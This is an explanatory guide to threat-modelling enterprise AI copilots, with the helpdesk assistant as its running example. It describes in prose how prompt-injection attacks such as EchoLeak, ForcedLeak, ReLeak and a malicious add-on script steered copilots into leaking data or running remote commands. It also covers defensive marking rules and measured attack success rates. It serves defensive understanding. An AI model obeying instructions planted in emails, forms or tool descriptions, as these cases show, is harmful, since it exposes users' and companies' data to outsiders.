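# Treating the output of enterprise AI copilots as untrusted input: a guide to threat modelling

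## What does it mean to treat a copilot's output as untrusted?

An enterprise copilot is an AI assistant that an organisation connects to its own data and tools. It runs on a large language model (LLM), a program that produces text by repeatedly predicting what comes next. Unlike a public chatbot, it can read the company's mail, documents and databases, and it can often act on internal systems, for instance by opening a support ticket.

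A common piece of security advice is to treat everything a copilot produces as untrusted. In security, "untrusted" means that an attacker may have chosen the data, so something has to check or confine it before anything acts on it. A copilot's answers should therefore be handled like a web form that a stranger filled in, even though the company pays for the copilot, controls who may use it and supplies the documents it reads. The route that text takes through the product helps explain why.

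### The path of a request

Microsoft 365 Copilot, which works inside Word, Outlook and Teams, is a well-documented example. According to Microsoft, when a user types a prompt, Copilot looks up related material in the organisation's data, a step called grounding, and sends the model the prompt with that material added. Microsoft says the material can include emails, files, chats, meetings, web pages and anything the user attaches. The practitioner blog Voitanos explains that the software coordinating these steps also adds a system prompt, a set of standing instructions that the user never sees. After the model answers, Copilot processes the response before returning it to the app and the user. Microsoft says this processing includes more grounding calls, security, compliance and privacy reviews, and "command generation".

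Suppose a company gives its staff an IT helpdesk assistant. It reads staff mail, helpdesk tickets and the company wiki. It can also query the asset database, which records who has which laptop and phone, write tickets, and start a password reset. Staff talk to it in a chat panel that displays formatted text and links. These capabilities are ordinary. Sanfilippo's *Copilot for Microsoft 365 Architecture*, for example, gives as a typical prompt a request to turn the last email from a colleague into a ticket in Jira, a product for tracking work.

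One request to the helpdesk copilot might go like this:

1. **Question.** An employee types that the VPN, the encrypted connection to the company network, stopped working after an update.
2. **Retrieval.** The copilot's software searches for related text. It finds a wiki page about the VPN, two old tickets from colleagues and an email from the VPN supplier. It also fetches the employee's laptop model from the asset database.
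3. **Assembly.** The software joins the system prompt, the question and everything it has found into a single text. This is the context, and it is all the text the model has to work from.
4. **Output.** The model produces more text. Part of it may be an answer for the employee. Part may be a tool call, which is also text: the name of a tool and the arguments for it, such as a ticket's title and priority.
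5. **Display or action.** Ordinary software takes over. The chat panel displays the answer and the ticket system creates the ticket. In many copilots the result of a tool call then joins the context, and the model runs again.

By step 4 the context contains text from the employee, two colleagues, a supplier, the editors of the wiki page and whoever wrote the system prompt. Only the employee asked the question, and the supplier doesn't work for the company. Microsoft's *Proactively identifying, assessing, and addressing risk in AI systems* therefore calls prompt assembly "a first-class security boundary", and warns that unexamined assumptions about trust build up there.

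### Sources, sinks and deputies

That Microsoft guidance is about threat modelling, the practice of working out early what could go wrong with a system and which risks matter most. The result is a threat model, a structured account of what the system must protect, who might attack it, how, and what will stop or limit them. Much of the work is finding trust boundaries, the points where data passes between parts of a system that deserve different degrees of trust. The classic example is the boundary between a visitor's browser and a company's web server. The server's programmers can't know who is typing, so they write the server to check whatever arrives.

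A source is any place where text enters a copilot's context, such as a mailbox or a wiki, and a sink is any component or person that acts on the output. Lecture slides from UT Austin, which credit OpenAI for the framing, describe every attack on an AI agent as a pairing of an untrusted source with a dangerous sink. An email is harmless if nobody can turn it into an action, as is a powerful tool that no outsider's text can reach. The slides name shells (programs that run typed commands), files, networks and cloud services as sinks. *OWASP Top 10 for LLM Applications 全覽* (Eric, 2026) also counts a person who reads the text. That seems right for a copilot, because an employee who follows bad instructions can do as much damage as a program that runs them.

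Attackers usually get from source to sink through prompt injection, which is text that makes a model follow an attacker's instructions. The injection is direct when the attacker types the text into the chat, and indirect when the text is in content the model has to read to do its job. David C, a technical director at the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, gives the example of a recruiter's system that scores CVs, and a candidate who, without using the system, hides a line in a CV telling the model to approve it.

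OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) defines prompt injection as an attacker placing instructions in outside content so that the model does something the user never requested. David C's *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)* instead defines it as developers joining their own instructions to untrusted content and then treating the response as if a firm boundary had kept the two apart. On that account, half of the vulnerability lies in how the application handles the output, which is the half its developers fully control.

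David C also recommends thinking of the model as a confused deputy, an older term for a privileged component that is induced to use its privileges on behalf of someone who lacks them. For example, the helpdesk copilot can start a password reset, but a stranger who emails an employee can't. If the stranger's email can get the copilot to start one, the copilot has become the stranger's deputy, and the reset system receives the request from a component it normally recognises.

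### Why output from inside the company still crosses a boundary

Treating a copilot's output as untrusted means assuming it deserves no more trust than the least trusted text in the model's context, unless something else in the system tracks where each part of the output came from. Other people's text passes through the model, so a sentence in the output may be a fair summary of a supplier's email, a phrase copied from it, or the result of an instruction hidden in it, and the output doesn't reliably show which. The output therefore crosses a trust boundary on its way to the chat panel or the ticket system, even when the model and both of those systems run inside the company.

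Vendors' assurances about data protection can obscure why a copilot's output is untrusted. Microsoft states that customers' data stays within the Microsoft 365 service boundary and that Copilot reads only what the signed-in user may read. These protections limit access to documents, but they don't ensure that the documents come from a trusted source. An employee is allowed to open a stranger's email in their inbox, so the copilot is allowed to retrieve it. EchoLeak, an attack in which a single email made Microsoft's Copilot leak files, began with this kind of permitted reading.

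Treating a copilot's output as untrusted limits what a designer may assume about it, even if the copilot is helpful and honest nearly all the time. Much of the case for doing so rests on the empirical premise that models can't reliably ignore instructions in the material they read. David C thinks they can't, because models don't inherently distinguish instructions from data. Even if they could, their ordinary mistakes would still be a reason to distrust their output.

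### OWASP's name for the failure

The Open Worldwide Application Security Project (OWASP), a non-profit foundation that publishes ranked lists of software risks, covers applications that skip the check in its 2025 Top 10 for LLM Applications. The fifth entry, *LLM05:2025 Improper Output Handling*, defines the problem as "insufficient validation, sanitization, and handling of the outputs generated by large language models" before those outputs go to other components and systems. Validation means checking that data has the form the receiver expects, and sanitisation means removing or neutralising anything the receiver might wrongly process as a command.

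OWASP reasons that prompt input can control what the model generates, so an application that passes the output along unchecked gives its users indirect access to functions they were never meant to have. With an enterprise copilot, someone without an account may also control part of the prompt. OWASP covers this case by listing indirect prompt injection among the conditions that make the flaw more damaging. Its first recommendation is to treat the model "as any other user" and to validate its responses before they reach backend functions. This is a good rule of thumb, though it gives the model slightly too much trust, because an ordinary user has logged in and can be held to account, unlike the author of a hostile email.

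In the first edition of the list, which Bugcrowd dates to August 2023, the entry was second and was called "Insecure Output Handling". Apart from that name, the defining sentence in OWASP's *LLM02* matches the 2025 one word for word. The 2023 text had two examples of the vulnerability: output that goes straight into a shell, and output that a browser runs as code. The 2025 text added database queries, file paths and email templates, and increased the number of recommended defences from three to seven.

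A third edition of OWASP's list came out in August 2026, though more than a week later Eric found that OWASP's main page for the list still presented the 2025 version as the latest. The entry is still called "Improper Output Handling". It is now LLM10:2026, the last of the ten, but its scope has widened. According to Invicti's *OWASP LLM Top 10 2026* (2026), it now explicitly covers terminals and programming tools that obey ANSI escape sequences, which are character codes that control a display instead of appearing on it. It also covers software that automatically fetches outside resources, such as images, when the model's output refers to them. In both cases, a developer could easily think that the output is only displayed.

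The drop from fifth to tenth is weak evidence that the risk has shrunk. Help Net Security's *OWASP 2026 LLM Top 10* (2026) reports that three-quarters of the ranking was based on a vote among practitioners and the rest on data from 6,639 recorded incidents. An entry can also fall because others have become more urgent, which is how Invicti, which sells application security tools, explains this drop. Excessive Agency, the risk of giving an AI system more power to act than it needs, for example, rose from sixth to third.

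The 2026 edition limits its scope to the model as a component inside an application. Once the model becomes an actor with tools and memory, OWASP refers readers to a separate list, the Top 10 for Agentic Applications. The helpdesk copilot is a component when it shows an answer about the VPN, but an actor when it starts a password reset, so a team building such a copilot would need both lists.

### Untrusted is not the same as wrong

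OWASP has always separated output handling from overreliance, which means depending too much on the accuracy and appropriateness of what a model produces. Overreliance had its own entry in 2023, in ninth place. According to the Isle of Man Cyber Security Centre, overreliance is about people trusting the output's accuracy, while output handling is about what the software does with the text before it reaches other systems.

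That division between people and software has since blurred. The ninth entry became Misinformation in 2025, and *Prompt Injection Remains Biggest LLM Risk, Despite Limited Incidents* (Coker, 2026) reports that in the 2026 edition, misinformation includes false output that influences an automated workflow or an agent's action as well as a human decision. Programs, too, can therefore rely on a model too much. The two problems still require different checks. Checking accuracy means finding out whether a statement is true, while checking security means assuming an attacker wrote the text and finding out whether it could do damage where it is going.

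Checking a copilot's output for accuracy and checking it for attacks can give opposite results. Suppose the helpdesk copilot answers a VPN question with the correct steps from the wiki, then adds a download link from a forged supplier email. A colleague who compared the answer with the wiki would approve it, even though the link is an attack. If the copilot instead says that the helpdesk closes at six when it closes at seven, the answer is wrong and may inconvenience someone, but no attacker gains anything.

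Some errors do harm without an attacker. If the copilot confuses two employees with similar names and starts a reset for the wrong one, the request is well formed and would pass a format check. In one OWASP scenario, a chatbot's ordinary response goes unchecked to an extension with administrative functions, and the extension shuts down for maintenance. A good part of the appeal of limiting what the output can trigger is that it helps against accidents like these as well as attacks.

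The label "untrusted" applies to all of a copilot's output because nobody can reliably pick out the hostile part by reading it. It doesn't mean that a particular answer is bad or that people must stop using the copilot. How much checking the output needs depends on the sink. The Isle of Man centre counts a draft that a person will review as one of the safer uses. Its higher-risk group includes anything that runs automatically, changes a system, queries a database or sends messages outside the organisation. The helpdesk copilot has uses in both groups, sometimes in response to a single question.

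## Who can influence what a copilot writes?

How far to trust a copilot's output depends on who could put text in front of the model. For most enterprise copilots, that includes many more people than those with accounts, because anyone who knows an employee's email address can do it. Microsoft's threat-modelling guidance advises teams to map where untrusted data enters a system, and to treat every point where outside data can influence prompts, memory or actions as high-risk by default. For a copilot like the helpdesk assistant, with a few common extras, the map might look like the table below. Products differ in how much retrieved text they display, so the last column is a judgement about ordinary use.

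| Source | Who can write to it | Outside the company? | Would the user notice? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Inbound email | Anyone who has an employee's address | Yes | Unlikely, as the copilot may read a message nobody has opened |
| Calendar invitation | Anyone who can invite the employee | Yes | The title perhaps, the full description rarely |
| Customer form or ticket | Anyone who can reach the form, often without logging in | Yes | Only by reading the whole record |
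| Shared document or wiki page | Everyone with editing rights, and the authors of files that came from elsewhere | Sometimes | Only if the text is visible and the user reads it |
| Public code issue | Anyone with an account on the hosting site | Yes | Only by reading the issue before the copilot does |
| Web page | Its owner, and anyone who can post comments there | Yes | Rarely, because the copilot opens the page |
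| Link that pre-fills a prompt | Whoever made the link | Usually | Perhaps, but only after clicking |
| Tool description | Whoever runs the tool's server | Often | Rarely |
| Tool result | Anyone who can write to the data behind the tool | Depends on the tool | Rarely |
| Add-on | Its author, and anyone who altered it later | Often | The user knows it is there, but not what is in it |
| Training data | Anyone whose text the model's maker collected | Mostly | No |

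### Text that arrives uninvited

Email is the easiest way in, because the sender needs no permission and the recipient needn't open the message. AIAIAI.FYI's *Cato AI Labs details three ReLeak zero-click attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026) describes a recent example. The attacker's email sat unopened in the inbox until the employee asked Copilot for something legitimate and Copilot retrieved the email. Security researchers call this a zero-click attack, because the victim only has to use the product normally. Microsoft fixed the three flaws between 17 September and 15 November 2026, and Cato's researchers knew of no real attacks that used them.

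Some agents run without a user who might notice something wrong. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* warns against setups like that of a customer-service agent that any incoming email could trigger. Calendar invitations deserve the same suspicion as email, because many calendar programs add an invitation before the recipient accepts it, and a copilot that summarises tomorrow's meetings will read the description.

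Web forms are easier to overlook, because what strangers type into them ends up in a company database. In 2025 Noma Security found a flaw in Agentforce, Salesforce's platform for building AI agents, and named it ForcedLeak. The flaw affected any organisation that used Agentforce with Web-to-Lead switched on (The Hacker News, *Salesforce Patches Critical ForcedLeak*, 2025). Web-to-Lead lets potential customers leave their details in a public form, which Salesforce saves among the company's sales records. The form's description field accepts up to 42,000 characters (ThaiCERT, *ForcedLeak Vulnerability in Salesforce Agentforce Risks CRM Data Exposure via Prompt Injection*, 2025), far more than a sales enquiry needs.

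In the attack described in SecurityWeek's *Salesforce AI Hack Enabled CRM Data Theft*, an outsider submitted a lead form containing instructions, which took effect only when an employee asked Agentforce to process the lead. The agent then collected data from the sales records and sent it to an outside server. The researchers also found that Salesforce had let one of its trusted domains expire, so an attacker could have registered it and received the data at an address that looked legitimate.

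Two boundaries failed here. The agent treated a stranger's text as a company record, and its output could then leave the company. Salesforce fixed the second failure by recovering the domain and stopping agents from sending output to untrusted addresses. PromptArmor's *One key way Salesforce mitigates AI risk* reports that the Salesforce web app now removes untrusted links from an agent's response, but that the agents still act on text from the form.

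That control is sensible, but it covers only one way for data to leave. In April 2026, Security Boulevard's *Microsoft and Salesforce Patch AI Agent Flaws That Could Leak Sensitive Data* described researchers again attacking Agentforce through a public lead form, this time sending the data out by email. A form in SharePoint, Microsoft's document-sharing product, allowed a similar attack through Copilot. Both companies have patched these flaws. Closing the entry point would be much harder, because public forms exist to let strangers write to the company.

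### Text that the user brings in

A document's location in the company's files is weak evidence of who wrote it, because suppliers send contracts, applicants send CVs, and colleagues save both to shared folders. Lahav (2026), in *Breaking the M365 Copilot Sandbox with ChatMate*, showed that one malicious file could give an attacker a live channel into a chat session once a user asked Microsoft's Copilot about the file. The attacker could then send prompts, read the replies and decide what to ask next. These prompts went directly into the context, so a list of the documents that Copilot had read would not have included them.

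Developers have a similar problem with public code repositories, where anyone with an account can open an issue, a note that reports a bug or requests a change. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a demonstration in which a public issue contained a request for information from a private repository. The coding assistant handling the issue could read that repository because the developer using it could, and it posted the information as a public comment. A ban on public posting would have prevented the leak if it had taken effect once the assistant's context contained both a stranger's text and private data.

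Some copilots also accept a prompt inside a web link, so whoever creates the link can write text where the software expects the user's question. The Hacker News' *Researchers Reveal Reprompt Attack Allowing Single-Click Data Exfiltration From Microsoft Copilot* (2026) describes an attack that needed only one click on a genuine Microsoft link. The attack didn't affect enterprise customers of Microsoft 365 Copilot, but the Cloud Security Alliance reports that a later flaw, SearchLeak, used the same kind of link against Copilot's enterprise search.

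### Tools, add-ons and training data

Before a model can call a tool, the software has to give it a description of what the tool does. Whoever runs the tool's server writes that description, which also becomes part of the model's context. Many AI assistants connect to such servers through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that Anthropic introduced in November 2024. *Model Context Protocol Threat Modeling and Analyzing Vulnerabilities to Prompt Injection* (Huang, Huang and colleagues, 2026) tested seven applications that use MCP and found that five had no static validation, meaning they didn't check a description before giving it to the model. Users seldom see the full description while a tool is in use. An earlier study that the paper cites examined 1,899 open-source MCP servers and found signs of tool poisoning (malicious instructions in a tool's description) in 5.5% of them.

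A tool's results are only as trustworthy as the data behind them. A web search returns text written by strangers. If staff can name their own laptops, even the helpdesk copilot's asset database returns text that any employee may have chosen.

Attackers can reach a copilot through add-ons, which can seem safe because users install many of them themselves. Copilot Cowork, a Microsoft 365 agent that works with the user's permissions, accepts add-ons called Skills, which can include scripts. PromptArmor's *Copilot Cowork Sandbox Bypass Gives Attackers Remote Control* describes a user who finds a Skill online for comparing documents and asks Cowork to check a contract against a proposal. Cowork runs the Skill's scripts and produces a full report of the inconsistencies. One script also fetches commands from the attacker's server, runs them and sends back the results, which could include Outlook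 mail and SharePoint files. Pressing the stop button didn't end the attack, because background processes kept running.

The sandbox, a confined environment, should have blocked access to the attacker's server but failed to. Microsoft had mitigated the flaw by 19 August 2026, eight weeks after learning of it. How the attacker got in matters just as much. The user chose the Skill and it did the job they wanted, so they had no obvious reason to suspect it. Colleagues can also share Skills, and the next person to run one may not know that it came from a stranger. A company that reviews software before staff install it should probably review Skills too.

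Training data shapes the model before anyone uses it. Moia, Sanz and colleagues (2025), in *LLM in the Middle*, note that this data comes largely from the public internet, and sometimes from an organisation's own data through fine-tuning, which is further training on a narrower set of examples. Anyone who publishes online might therefore contribute to the training data, although this is a slower and less certain way to influence a copilot than sending an email.

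### The influence rule

The term "untrusted" assumes the influence rule, which is that an output deserves no more trust than the least trusted item in its context. The idea comes from information-flow control, a branch of computer security that labels data and carries the labels along as programs combine it. An integrity label records how far to trust a piece of data, and a confidentiality label records who may see it.

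*Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) applies these labels to AI agents. Its simplest integrity label has two values, trusted and untrusted. A more detailed label is the set of people who could have written the data. If Ann and Bob can edit one document, and Bob and Carla can edit another, any of the three could have contributed to a text made from both.

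With numbers in place of sets, where a higher number means more trust, the rule is a minimum:

**integrity(output) ≤ min(integrity of every item in the context)**

Suppose the helpdesk copilot's designers use three levels: 2 for text that only their own team can write, 1 for text that any employee can write, and 0 for text that anyone can write. A question about the VPN brings together:

- the system prompt, at level 2
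- a wiki page that any employee can edit, at level 1
- one email from outside the company, at level 0

The minimum of 2, 1 and 0 is 0, so whatever receives the output should handle it as though the email's sender might have chosen every word, even though the other two items came from inside the company. Without the email, the minimum would be 1, and the only possible authors would be the company's own staff.

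Adding trusted text, such as ten more wiki pages or a sterner system prompt, doesn't raise the minimum above 0. A text's level depends on who wrote it, so an outside email stays at 0 when a colleague forwards it. In an ordinary chat the history remains in the context, so an email the copilot reads in the morning lowers the level of every later answer in that chat. If the copilot saves an answer and reads it again another day, the saved text should keep its level.

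Costa and colleagues assume that the system prompt, the tool descriptions and the model itself are trustworthy. This is doubtful for tool descriptions when an outside party runs the server, and it would be safer to give each description its author's level. The assumption about the model is harder to drop, because if training data counted as part of the context, every output would be at level 0 and the rule would treat them all the same.

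### Why use such a pessimistic rule?

Most outputs aren't steered by anyone. Nearly all email is harmless, many injections fail, and the answer about the VPN would usually be much the same without the supplier's message. Costa and colleagues call their version of the rule sound, meaning it errs on the side of distrust, but concede it "may be overly conservative".

Defenders still need the rule because they can't see which inputs influenced a model's reply. In an ordinary program, a developer can follow a value from input to output. If a script copies a ticket number into the subject line of a fixed message, the ticket doesn't affect the rest of the message. A language model's reply can't be traced this way, since any part of the context may affect any part of the reply. Comparing the reply with its sources would catch a copied sentence, but an email can steer a reply that shares none of its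 words, so defenders can be certain only of which texts the model received.

An attacker can rewrite a message until it steers the copilot's output, then send it to as many employees as they like. Steered outputs are rare in everyday use, but that offers little reassurance against someone who is trying to produce them.

A team can make the rule less restrictive by basing each reply on fewer items. Costa and colleagues cite a method by Siddiqui and others that identifies which items influenced a reply, then generates the reply again from those items alone. The new reply is about as useful as the old one and may get a higher label, because the minimum is taken over fewer items. A team can get some of this benefit by keeping unnecessary text out of the context. If the wiki page answers the VPN question, leaving out the supplier's email raises the output's label from 0 to 1.

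If a copilot searches the mailbox on every request, nearly all its outputs will be at level 0. The rule then can't separate good outputs from bad ones, so the team has to decide what a level-0 output may do. Software can carry the labels and block actions automatically, but even without it, the team can work through the levels on paper to see which tool calls a stranger might be able to cause.

### Insiders and honest mistakes

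An employee with few permissions can be an attacker too. *Multi-Stage Prompt Inference Attacks on Enterprise LLM Systems* (Balashov, Ponomarova and Zhai, 2025) considers an insider who extracts the contents of a document they aren't allowed to open by asking the company's assistant a series of questions. In one simulation, the attacker reconstructed a 500-word confidential report with 90% accuracy over 20 turns. This only works if the assistant can read documents that the person asking can't. If a copilot can read only what the signed-in user can, as Microsoft says is true of its Copilot, the insider would do better to write something that a more privileged colleague's copilot will retrieve.

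With the helpdesk copilot, a temporary worker who can edit the wiki but can't reset anyone else's password might alter the VPN page. When an administrator asks about the VPN, the copilot reads that page while working with the administrator's permissions. A two-value trust label handles this badly, because the wiki must be marked as either fully trusted or no more trusted than a stranger's email. Microsoft and GitHub label files from private code repositories as trusted. That seems reasonable where few people can write to a repository, although one of them could still be hostile. The middle level is a better fit for a wiki that thousands of people can edit.

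Much of the text that misleads a copilot was written in good faith. An old wiki page may recommend a VPN setting that the company has since dropped. A supplier may end an email by asking the human reader to "please confirm by return", and the copilot may send the confirmation. Costa and colleagues add that models misread users' intentions and make needless tool calls even when all the data is trustworthy. The rule therefore sets only an upper limit. In a context at level 2, outsiders and ordinary staff cannot steer the output, but it can still be wrong.

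An agent can also leak data by mistake, without an attacker or a hidden instruction. In an example from Microsoft, Alex asks an agent to deal with unanswered emails. One, from Priya, contains a preview of the quarterly sales figures. Another is from Marco, who is curious about the figures but isn't allowed to see them yet. An agent working alone might include them in its reply to him. Confidentiality labels would catch this, because text based on both emails may go only to people who could read both, in this case only Alex. Microsoft's rule of thumb is to assume that an agent can do by mistake anything it can do at a user's request.

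## Can the model be made reliable enough to trust?

The influence rule would matter much less if models reliably ignored instructions in the material they read, such as a hostile line in a supplier's email. Models have become far better at this since 2025, and the best now resist nearly all the attacks that worked on earlier models. But researchers keep finding new attacks, and nobody can put a firm upper limit on how often a new one will succeed.

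### Why a model can't enforce the line

Many security specialists expect prompt injection to become preventable, as SQL injection did. In that older attack, text from a web form reaches a database and runs as a command. Developers can prevent it with parameterised queries, in which the program sends the database a command with a gap in it and sends the visitor's text separately to fill the gap. The database treats that text only as a value, never as part of the command. If the helpdesk looks up laptops this way, nothing typed in the surname field can delete a record.

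In December 2025, David C argued that this comparison is dangerous because a language model has no equivalent of the gap. It receives its whole context as one sequence of tokens (words or pieces of words) and predicts the next one. Developers can add markers to show where an email begins, but the markers are also tokens, and the model has only learned to treat them in a certain way.

He therefore calls the model an "inherently confusable deputy". Developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but with a language model he thinks they can only reduce the likelihood and impact of an attack. He adds that a system that can't tolerate the remaining risk may not be a good use for a language model. Google's security team takes a similar view of its own products. In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) writes that indirect prompt injection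 isn't a technical problem that a company solves and then leaves behind.

David C's argument is convincing on whether resistance to injected instructions can be guaranteed, but less convincing on how often a model will follow them. Nothing in next-token prediction stops a model from learning to disregard injected instructions 99.99% of the time, just as models learn grammar without a component that enforces it. But a developer can only check a model's reliability by running tests, and the result depends on how good the attacks in the tests were. With a parameterised query, the developer can inspect the code and be confident that it will hold against inputs nobody has tried.

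### Training, marking and detection

Model makers train their models to rank instructions by source, in an order called the instruction hierarchy. The system prompt outranks the user's request, and text inside a document or tool result should have no authority. Training includes examples where these levels conflict, and the model is rewarded for following the higher-ranked instruction. According to OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026), the company trains its models against GPT-Red, an automated attacker, while trying to preserve their ability to finish legitimate tasks. Preserving that ability matters because a copilot that avoided attacks by ignoring every email could not help users read their mail.

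Developers can also mark outside text to help the model distinguish it from instructions. Microsoft calls its version Spotlighting. For example, the software might put a special character between the words of an email, and the system prompt would include an instruction never to obey text marked this way. David C thinks such marking makes injection harder, and that even simple tags around outside content can help.

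Another approach is to detect attacks before the model reads them. Microsoft's Prompt Shields is a classifier, a separate model that flags prompts and documents that appear to contain an injection. It should catch paraphrases that a list of banned phrases would miss. David C warns against such lists because an attacker can reword a message in endless ways. But a classifier still relies on the text, and both EchoLeak and ReLeak got past Microsoft's classifier. David C advises buyers to be wary of any product that claims to "stop" injection, and to prefer suppliers who understand how their product reduces it.

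These defences looked better in 2024 and early 2025 than they were, because developers mostly tested them against fixed collections of known attacks. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, 2025) tested 12 published defences against adaptive attacks, in which the attacker tries a text, looks at how the system responds, revises the text and tries again. The researchers, several of whom worked at OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, used automated search, trained attacker models and a competition with over 500 human participants. They assumed that the attacker had plenty of computing power.

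Attacks had success rates near zero against most of the 12 defences in the original evaluations, but the new attacks succeeded more than 90% of the time against most of them. Some of the defences were meant to stop users from misusing a chatbot, while others, including Spotlighting, were meant to stop prompt injection. Nasr and colleagues describe Spotlighting as marking the trusted text, the reverse of the arrangement above. Fixed attacks succeeded against it as little as 1% of the time, while adaptive attacks succeeded over 95% of the time. The results were the same for a defence that repeats the user's request after the untrusted text. One successful attack presented the attacker's task as a required step in the user's task, so reminding the model of the user's task didn't help.

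The results for particular models are out of date, but they changed what counts as evidence. Replaying old attacks can show that a model is vulnerable, but a good score is only weak evidence that it is robust.

### The Gray Swan competition

The largest public measurement so far comes from a three-week competition run by Gray Swan, a company that tests AI systems by attacking them. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) reports that 464 participants attempted about 272,000 attacks on 13 models. The scenarios covered agents that call tools, write code or operate a computer through its screen.

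In each scenario, the participant controlled one piece of outside content, such as an email or a comment in a file, and had to cause a particular harmful action. In one scenario, a user asked an assistant to check for urgent mail. The participant wrote part of a marketing email, and won if the assistant marked a message about a critical deadline as read and left it out of its summary. In nearly all the scenarios, the assistant's reply to the user also had to show no sign that anything had happened.

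Participants succeeded 8,648 times, or in about 3.2% of attempts. They succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Tool-calling agents, the group most like an enterprise copilot, had the highest overall rate at 4.8%, compared with 2.5% for coding agents.

A model's general ability was a poor guide to how well it resisted attacks. Dziemian and colleagues found only a weak, statistically insignificant correlation between attack success rates and scores on a difficult science test. Gemini 2.5 Pro and Kimi K2 had similar science scores, but attacks succeeded 8.5% of the time against Gemini and 4.8% against Kimi. How a model is trained seems to matter more, so a company can't assume that the most capable model is also the hardest to manipulate.

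Attacks also transferred between models, mostly from those that were harder to attack to those that were easier. Attacks that had succeeded against Claude Opus 4.5 worked on the other models between 44% and 81% of the time, whereas none of those that had succeeded against Qwen3 VL, a much weaker target, worked on Opus. One participant's template succeeded, with small changes, in 21 of the 41 scenarios and on nine models. Keeping a copilot's underlying model secret therefore offers little protection.

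### Newer models and stronger attackers

By autumn 2026 the competition's attacks had largely stopped working on the best models. Kurakin, Karande and colleagues (2026), in *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms*, note that less than 1% of the attacks reused from Gray Swan's arena succeeded against recent Gemini models and some versions of Claude. In June 2026 Anthropic reported that its Claude Mythos 5 had the best result to date on a Gray Swan injection benchmark.

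OpenAI reports that GPT-6 Astra, which it released in September 2026, resisted 99.79% of indirect injection attempts in the company's own automated tests, up from 96.23% for its predecessor, GPT-5.6 Sol. The failure rate therefore fell about eighteenfold. Gray Swan also tested both models on 1,810 attacks chosen from its 2026 competitions. The estimated chance that at least one of 15 attempts would succeed, averaged over the scenarios, was 8.5% for Astra and 27.0% for Sol.

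That is real progress, but both tests are limited. Gray Swan's attacks came from earlier competitions, so they don't show what an attacker could achieve by targeting Astra specifically. The internal tests used GPT-Red, which OpenAI also uses in training, so they may be a poor guide to attackers who work differently. GPT-Red is still a strong attacker. OpenAI found that it could beat GPT-5.1 in 84% of scenarios on an internal copy of the Gray Swan arena, compared with 13% for human testers. Competitions that rely on human attackers may therefore understate what automated ones can do.

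Yin, Jin and colleagues (2026), in *Climbing the Hill*, trained a small open model to write injections. The standard fixed attack never worked on GPT-5.6-Terra or GPT-6-Luna, so a test that used only that attack would have given both a perfect score. The small model also failed against both before its training. After training, it succeeded within ten tries in 45.0% of test cases on GPT-5.6-Terra and 47.3% on GPT-6-Luna, even though it had never practised on GPT-6-Luna.

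In November 2026, Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind went further by using teams of AI agents as the attacker. Eight teams of two agents shared notes and a leaderboard of their best attempts, with up to 320 tries at each of 100 scenarios. The attackers' goal was always to make the model take a harmless action unrelated to the user's request. In one scenario, they had to get an assistant that was booking a tutoring session to record someone's blood pressure. The researchers chose harmless goals to test whether a model obeys text it should ignore, separately from whether it recognises and refuses something dangerous.

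Gemini 4 Argon, the most resistant model tested, withstood the first 150 attack attempts in 87% of scenarios and all 320 in 66%. For Gemini 3.8 Flash, the figures were 34% and 10%. Three open-weight models, which companies can run on their own computers, withstood all 320 in only 1% of scenarios. When weaker Gemini models ran the attacking teams, Gemini 4 Argon withstood the first 150 attempts in every scenario. Its score fell to 87% only when the attacking agents also ran on Gemini 4 Argon. A score of 100% may therefore mean only that nobody has yet tested the model against a strong enough attacker.

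Those tests ran with Google's product defences switched off, and models might refuse a plainly malicious action more often than a harmless one. The rates therefore don't estimate how often Gemini would do damage in a real product. Kurakin and colleagues ran a smaller experiment with the defences on, using an older model, Gemini 3.6 Flash, and a less capable attacker. The attacker succeeded in 6 of 80 scenarios within 25 tries. However, many of the actions an attacker would want from an enterprise copilot look routine, such as a helpdesk password reset, so a model's tendency to refuse plainly malicious actions may not help much.

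### What happens over many attempts

An attacker who fails can usually try again. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, and the attempts are independent, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is:

**P(at least one success) = 1 − (1 − p)ⁿ**

At a success rate of 0.5% per attempt, the lowest in the Gray Swan competition, an attacker who makes 200 attempts has about a 63% chance of succeeding at least once (1 − 0.995²⁰⁰). At 8.5%, the highest rate, eight attempts are enough to make success more likely than not.

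But attempts aren't really independent. The table compares the formula with tests that measured both single and repeated attempts. The figures for Claude Opus 4.5 come from The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals*, and those for Claude Opus 4.6 come from VentureBeat.

| Model | Source | Success on one attempt | Number of attempts | At least one success, if independent | At least one success, measured |
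|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | The Decoder | 4.7% | 10 | 38% | 33.6% |
| Claude Opus 4.5 | The Decoder | 4.7% | 100 | 99% | 63% |
| Claude Opus 4.6, operating a screen, no safeguards | VentureBeat | 17.8% | 200 | Almost 100% | 78.6% |
| GPT-5.6-Terra | Yin and colleagues | 18.3% | 10 | 87% | 45.0% |
| GPT-6-Luna | Yin and colleagues | 21.4% | 10 | 91% | 47.3% |

The formula overestimates the attacker's chance of success every time, probably because successes cluster: some tasks are easy to attack and others very hard, so an average rate describes neither. Participants in the Gray Swan competition beat Claude Opus 4.5 in only 13 of 37 scenarios. Suppose, for simplicity, that they spread their attempts evenly and that the other 24 scenarios were unbreakable. An overall success rate of 0.5% per attempt would then mean a rate of about 1.4% in each of the 13. In any one of those,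 200 attempts would have about a 94% chance of at least one success. For a scenario picked at random from all 37, the chance would be about 33%, compared with the formula's 63%.

This is only partly reassuring, because an attacker will concentrate on the tasks where attacks work best. A defender would also want to know which tasks those are. Even if the average success rate is 33%, a copilot could be safe when it summarises mail and almost certain to fail when it handles tickets. VentureBeat's figures for Claude Opus 4.6 show how wide the gap can be. An attack on the model in a restricted coding environment failed in all 200 attempts, even without added safeguards. When the model operated a screen, the success rate over 200 attempts was 78.6% without safeguards and still 57.1% with them.

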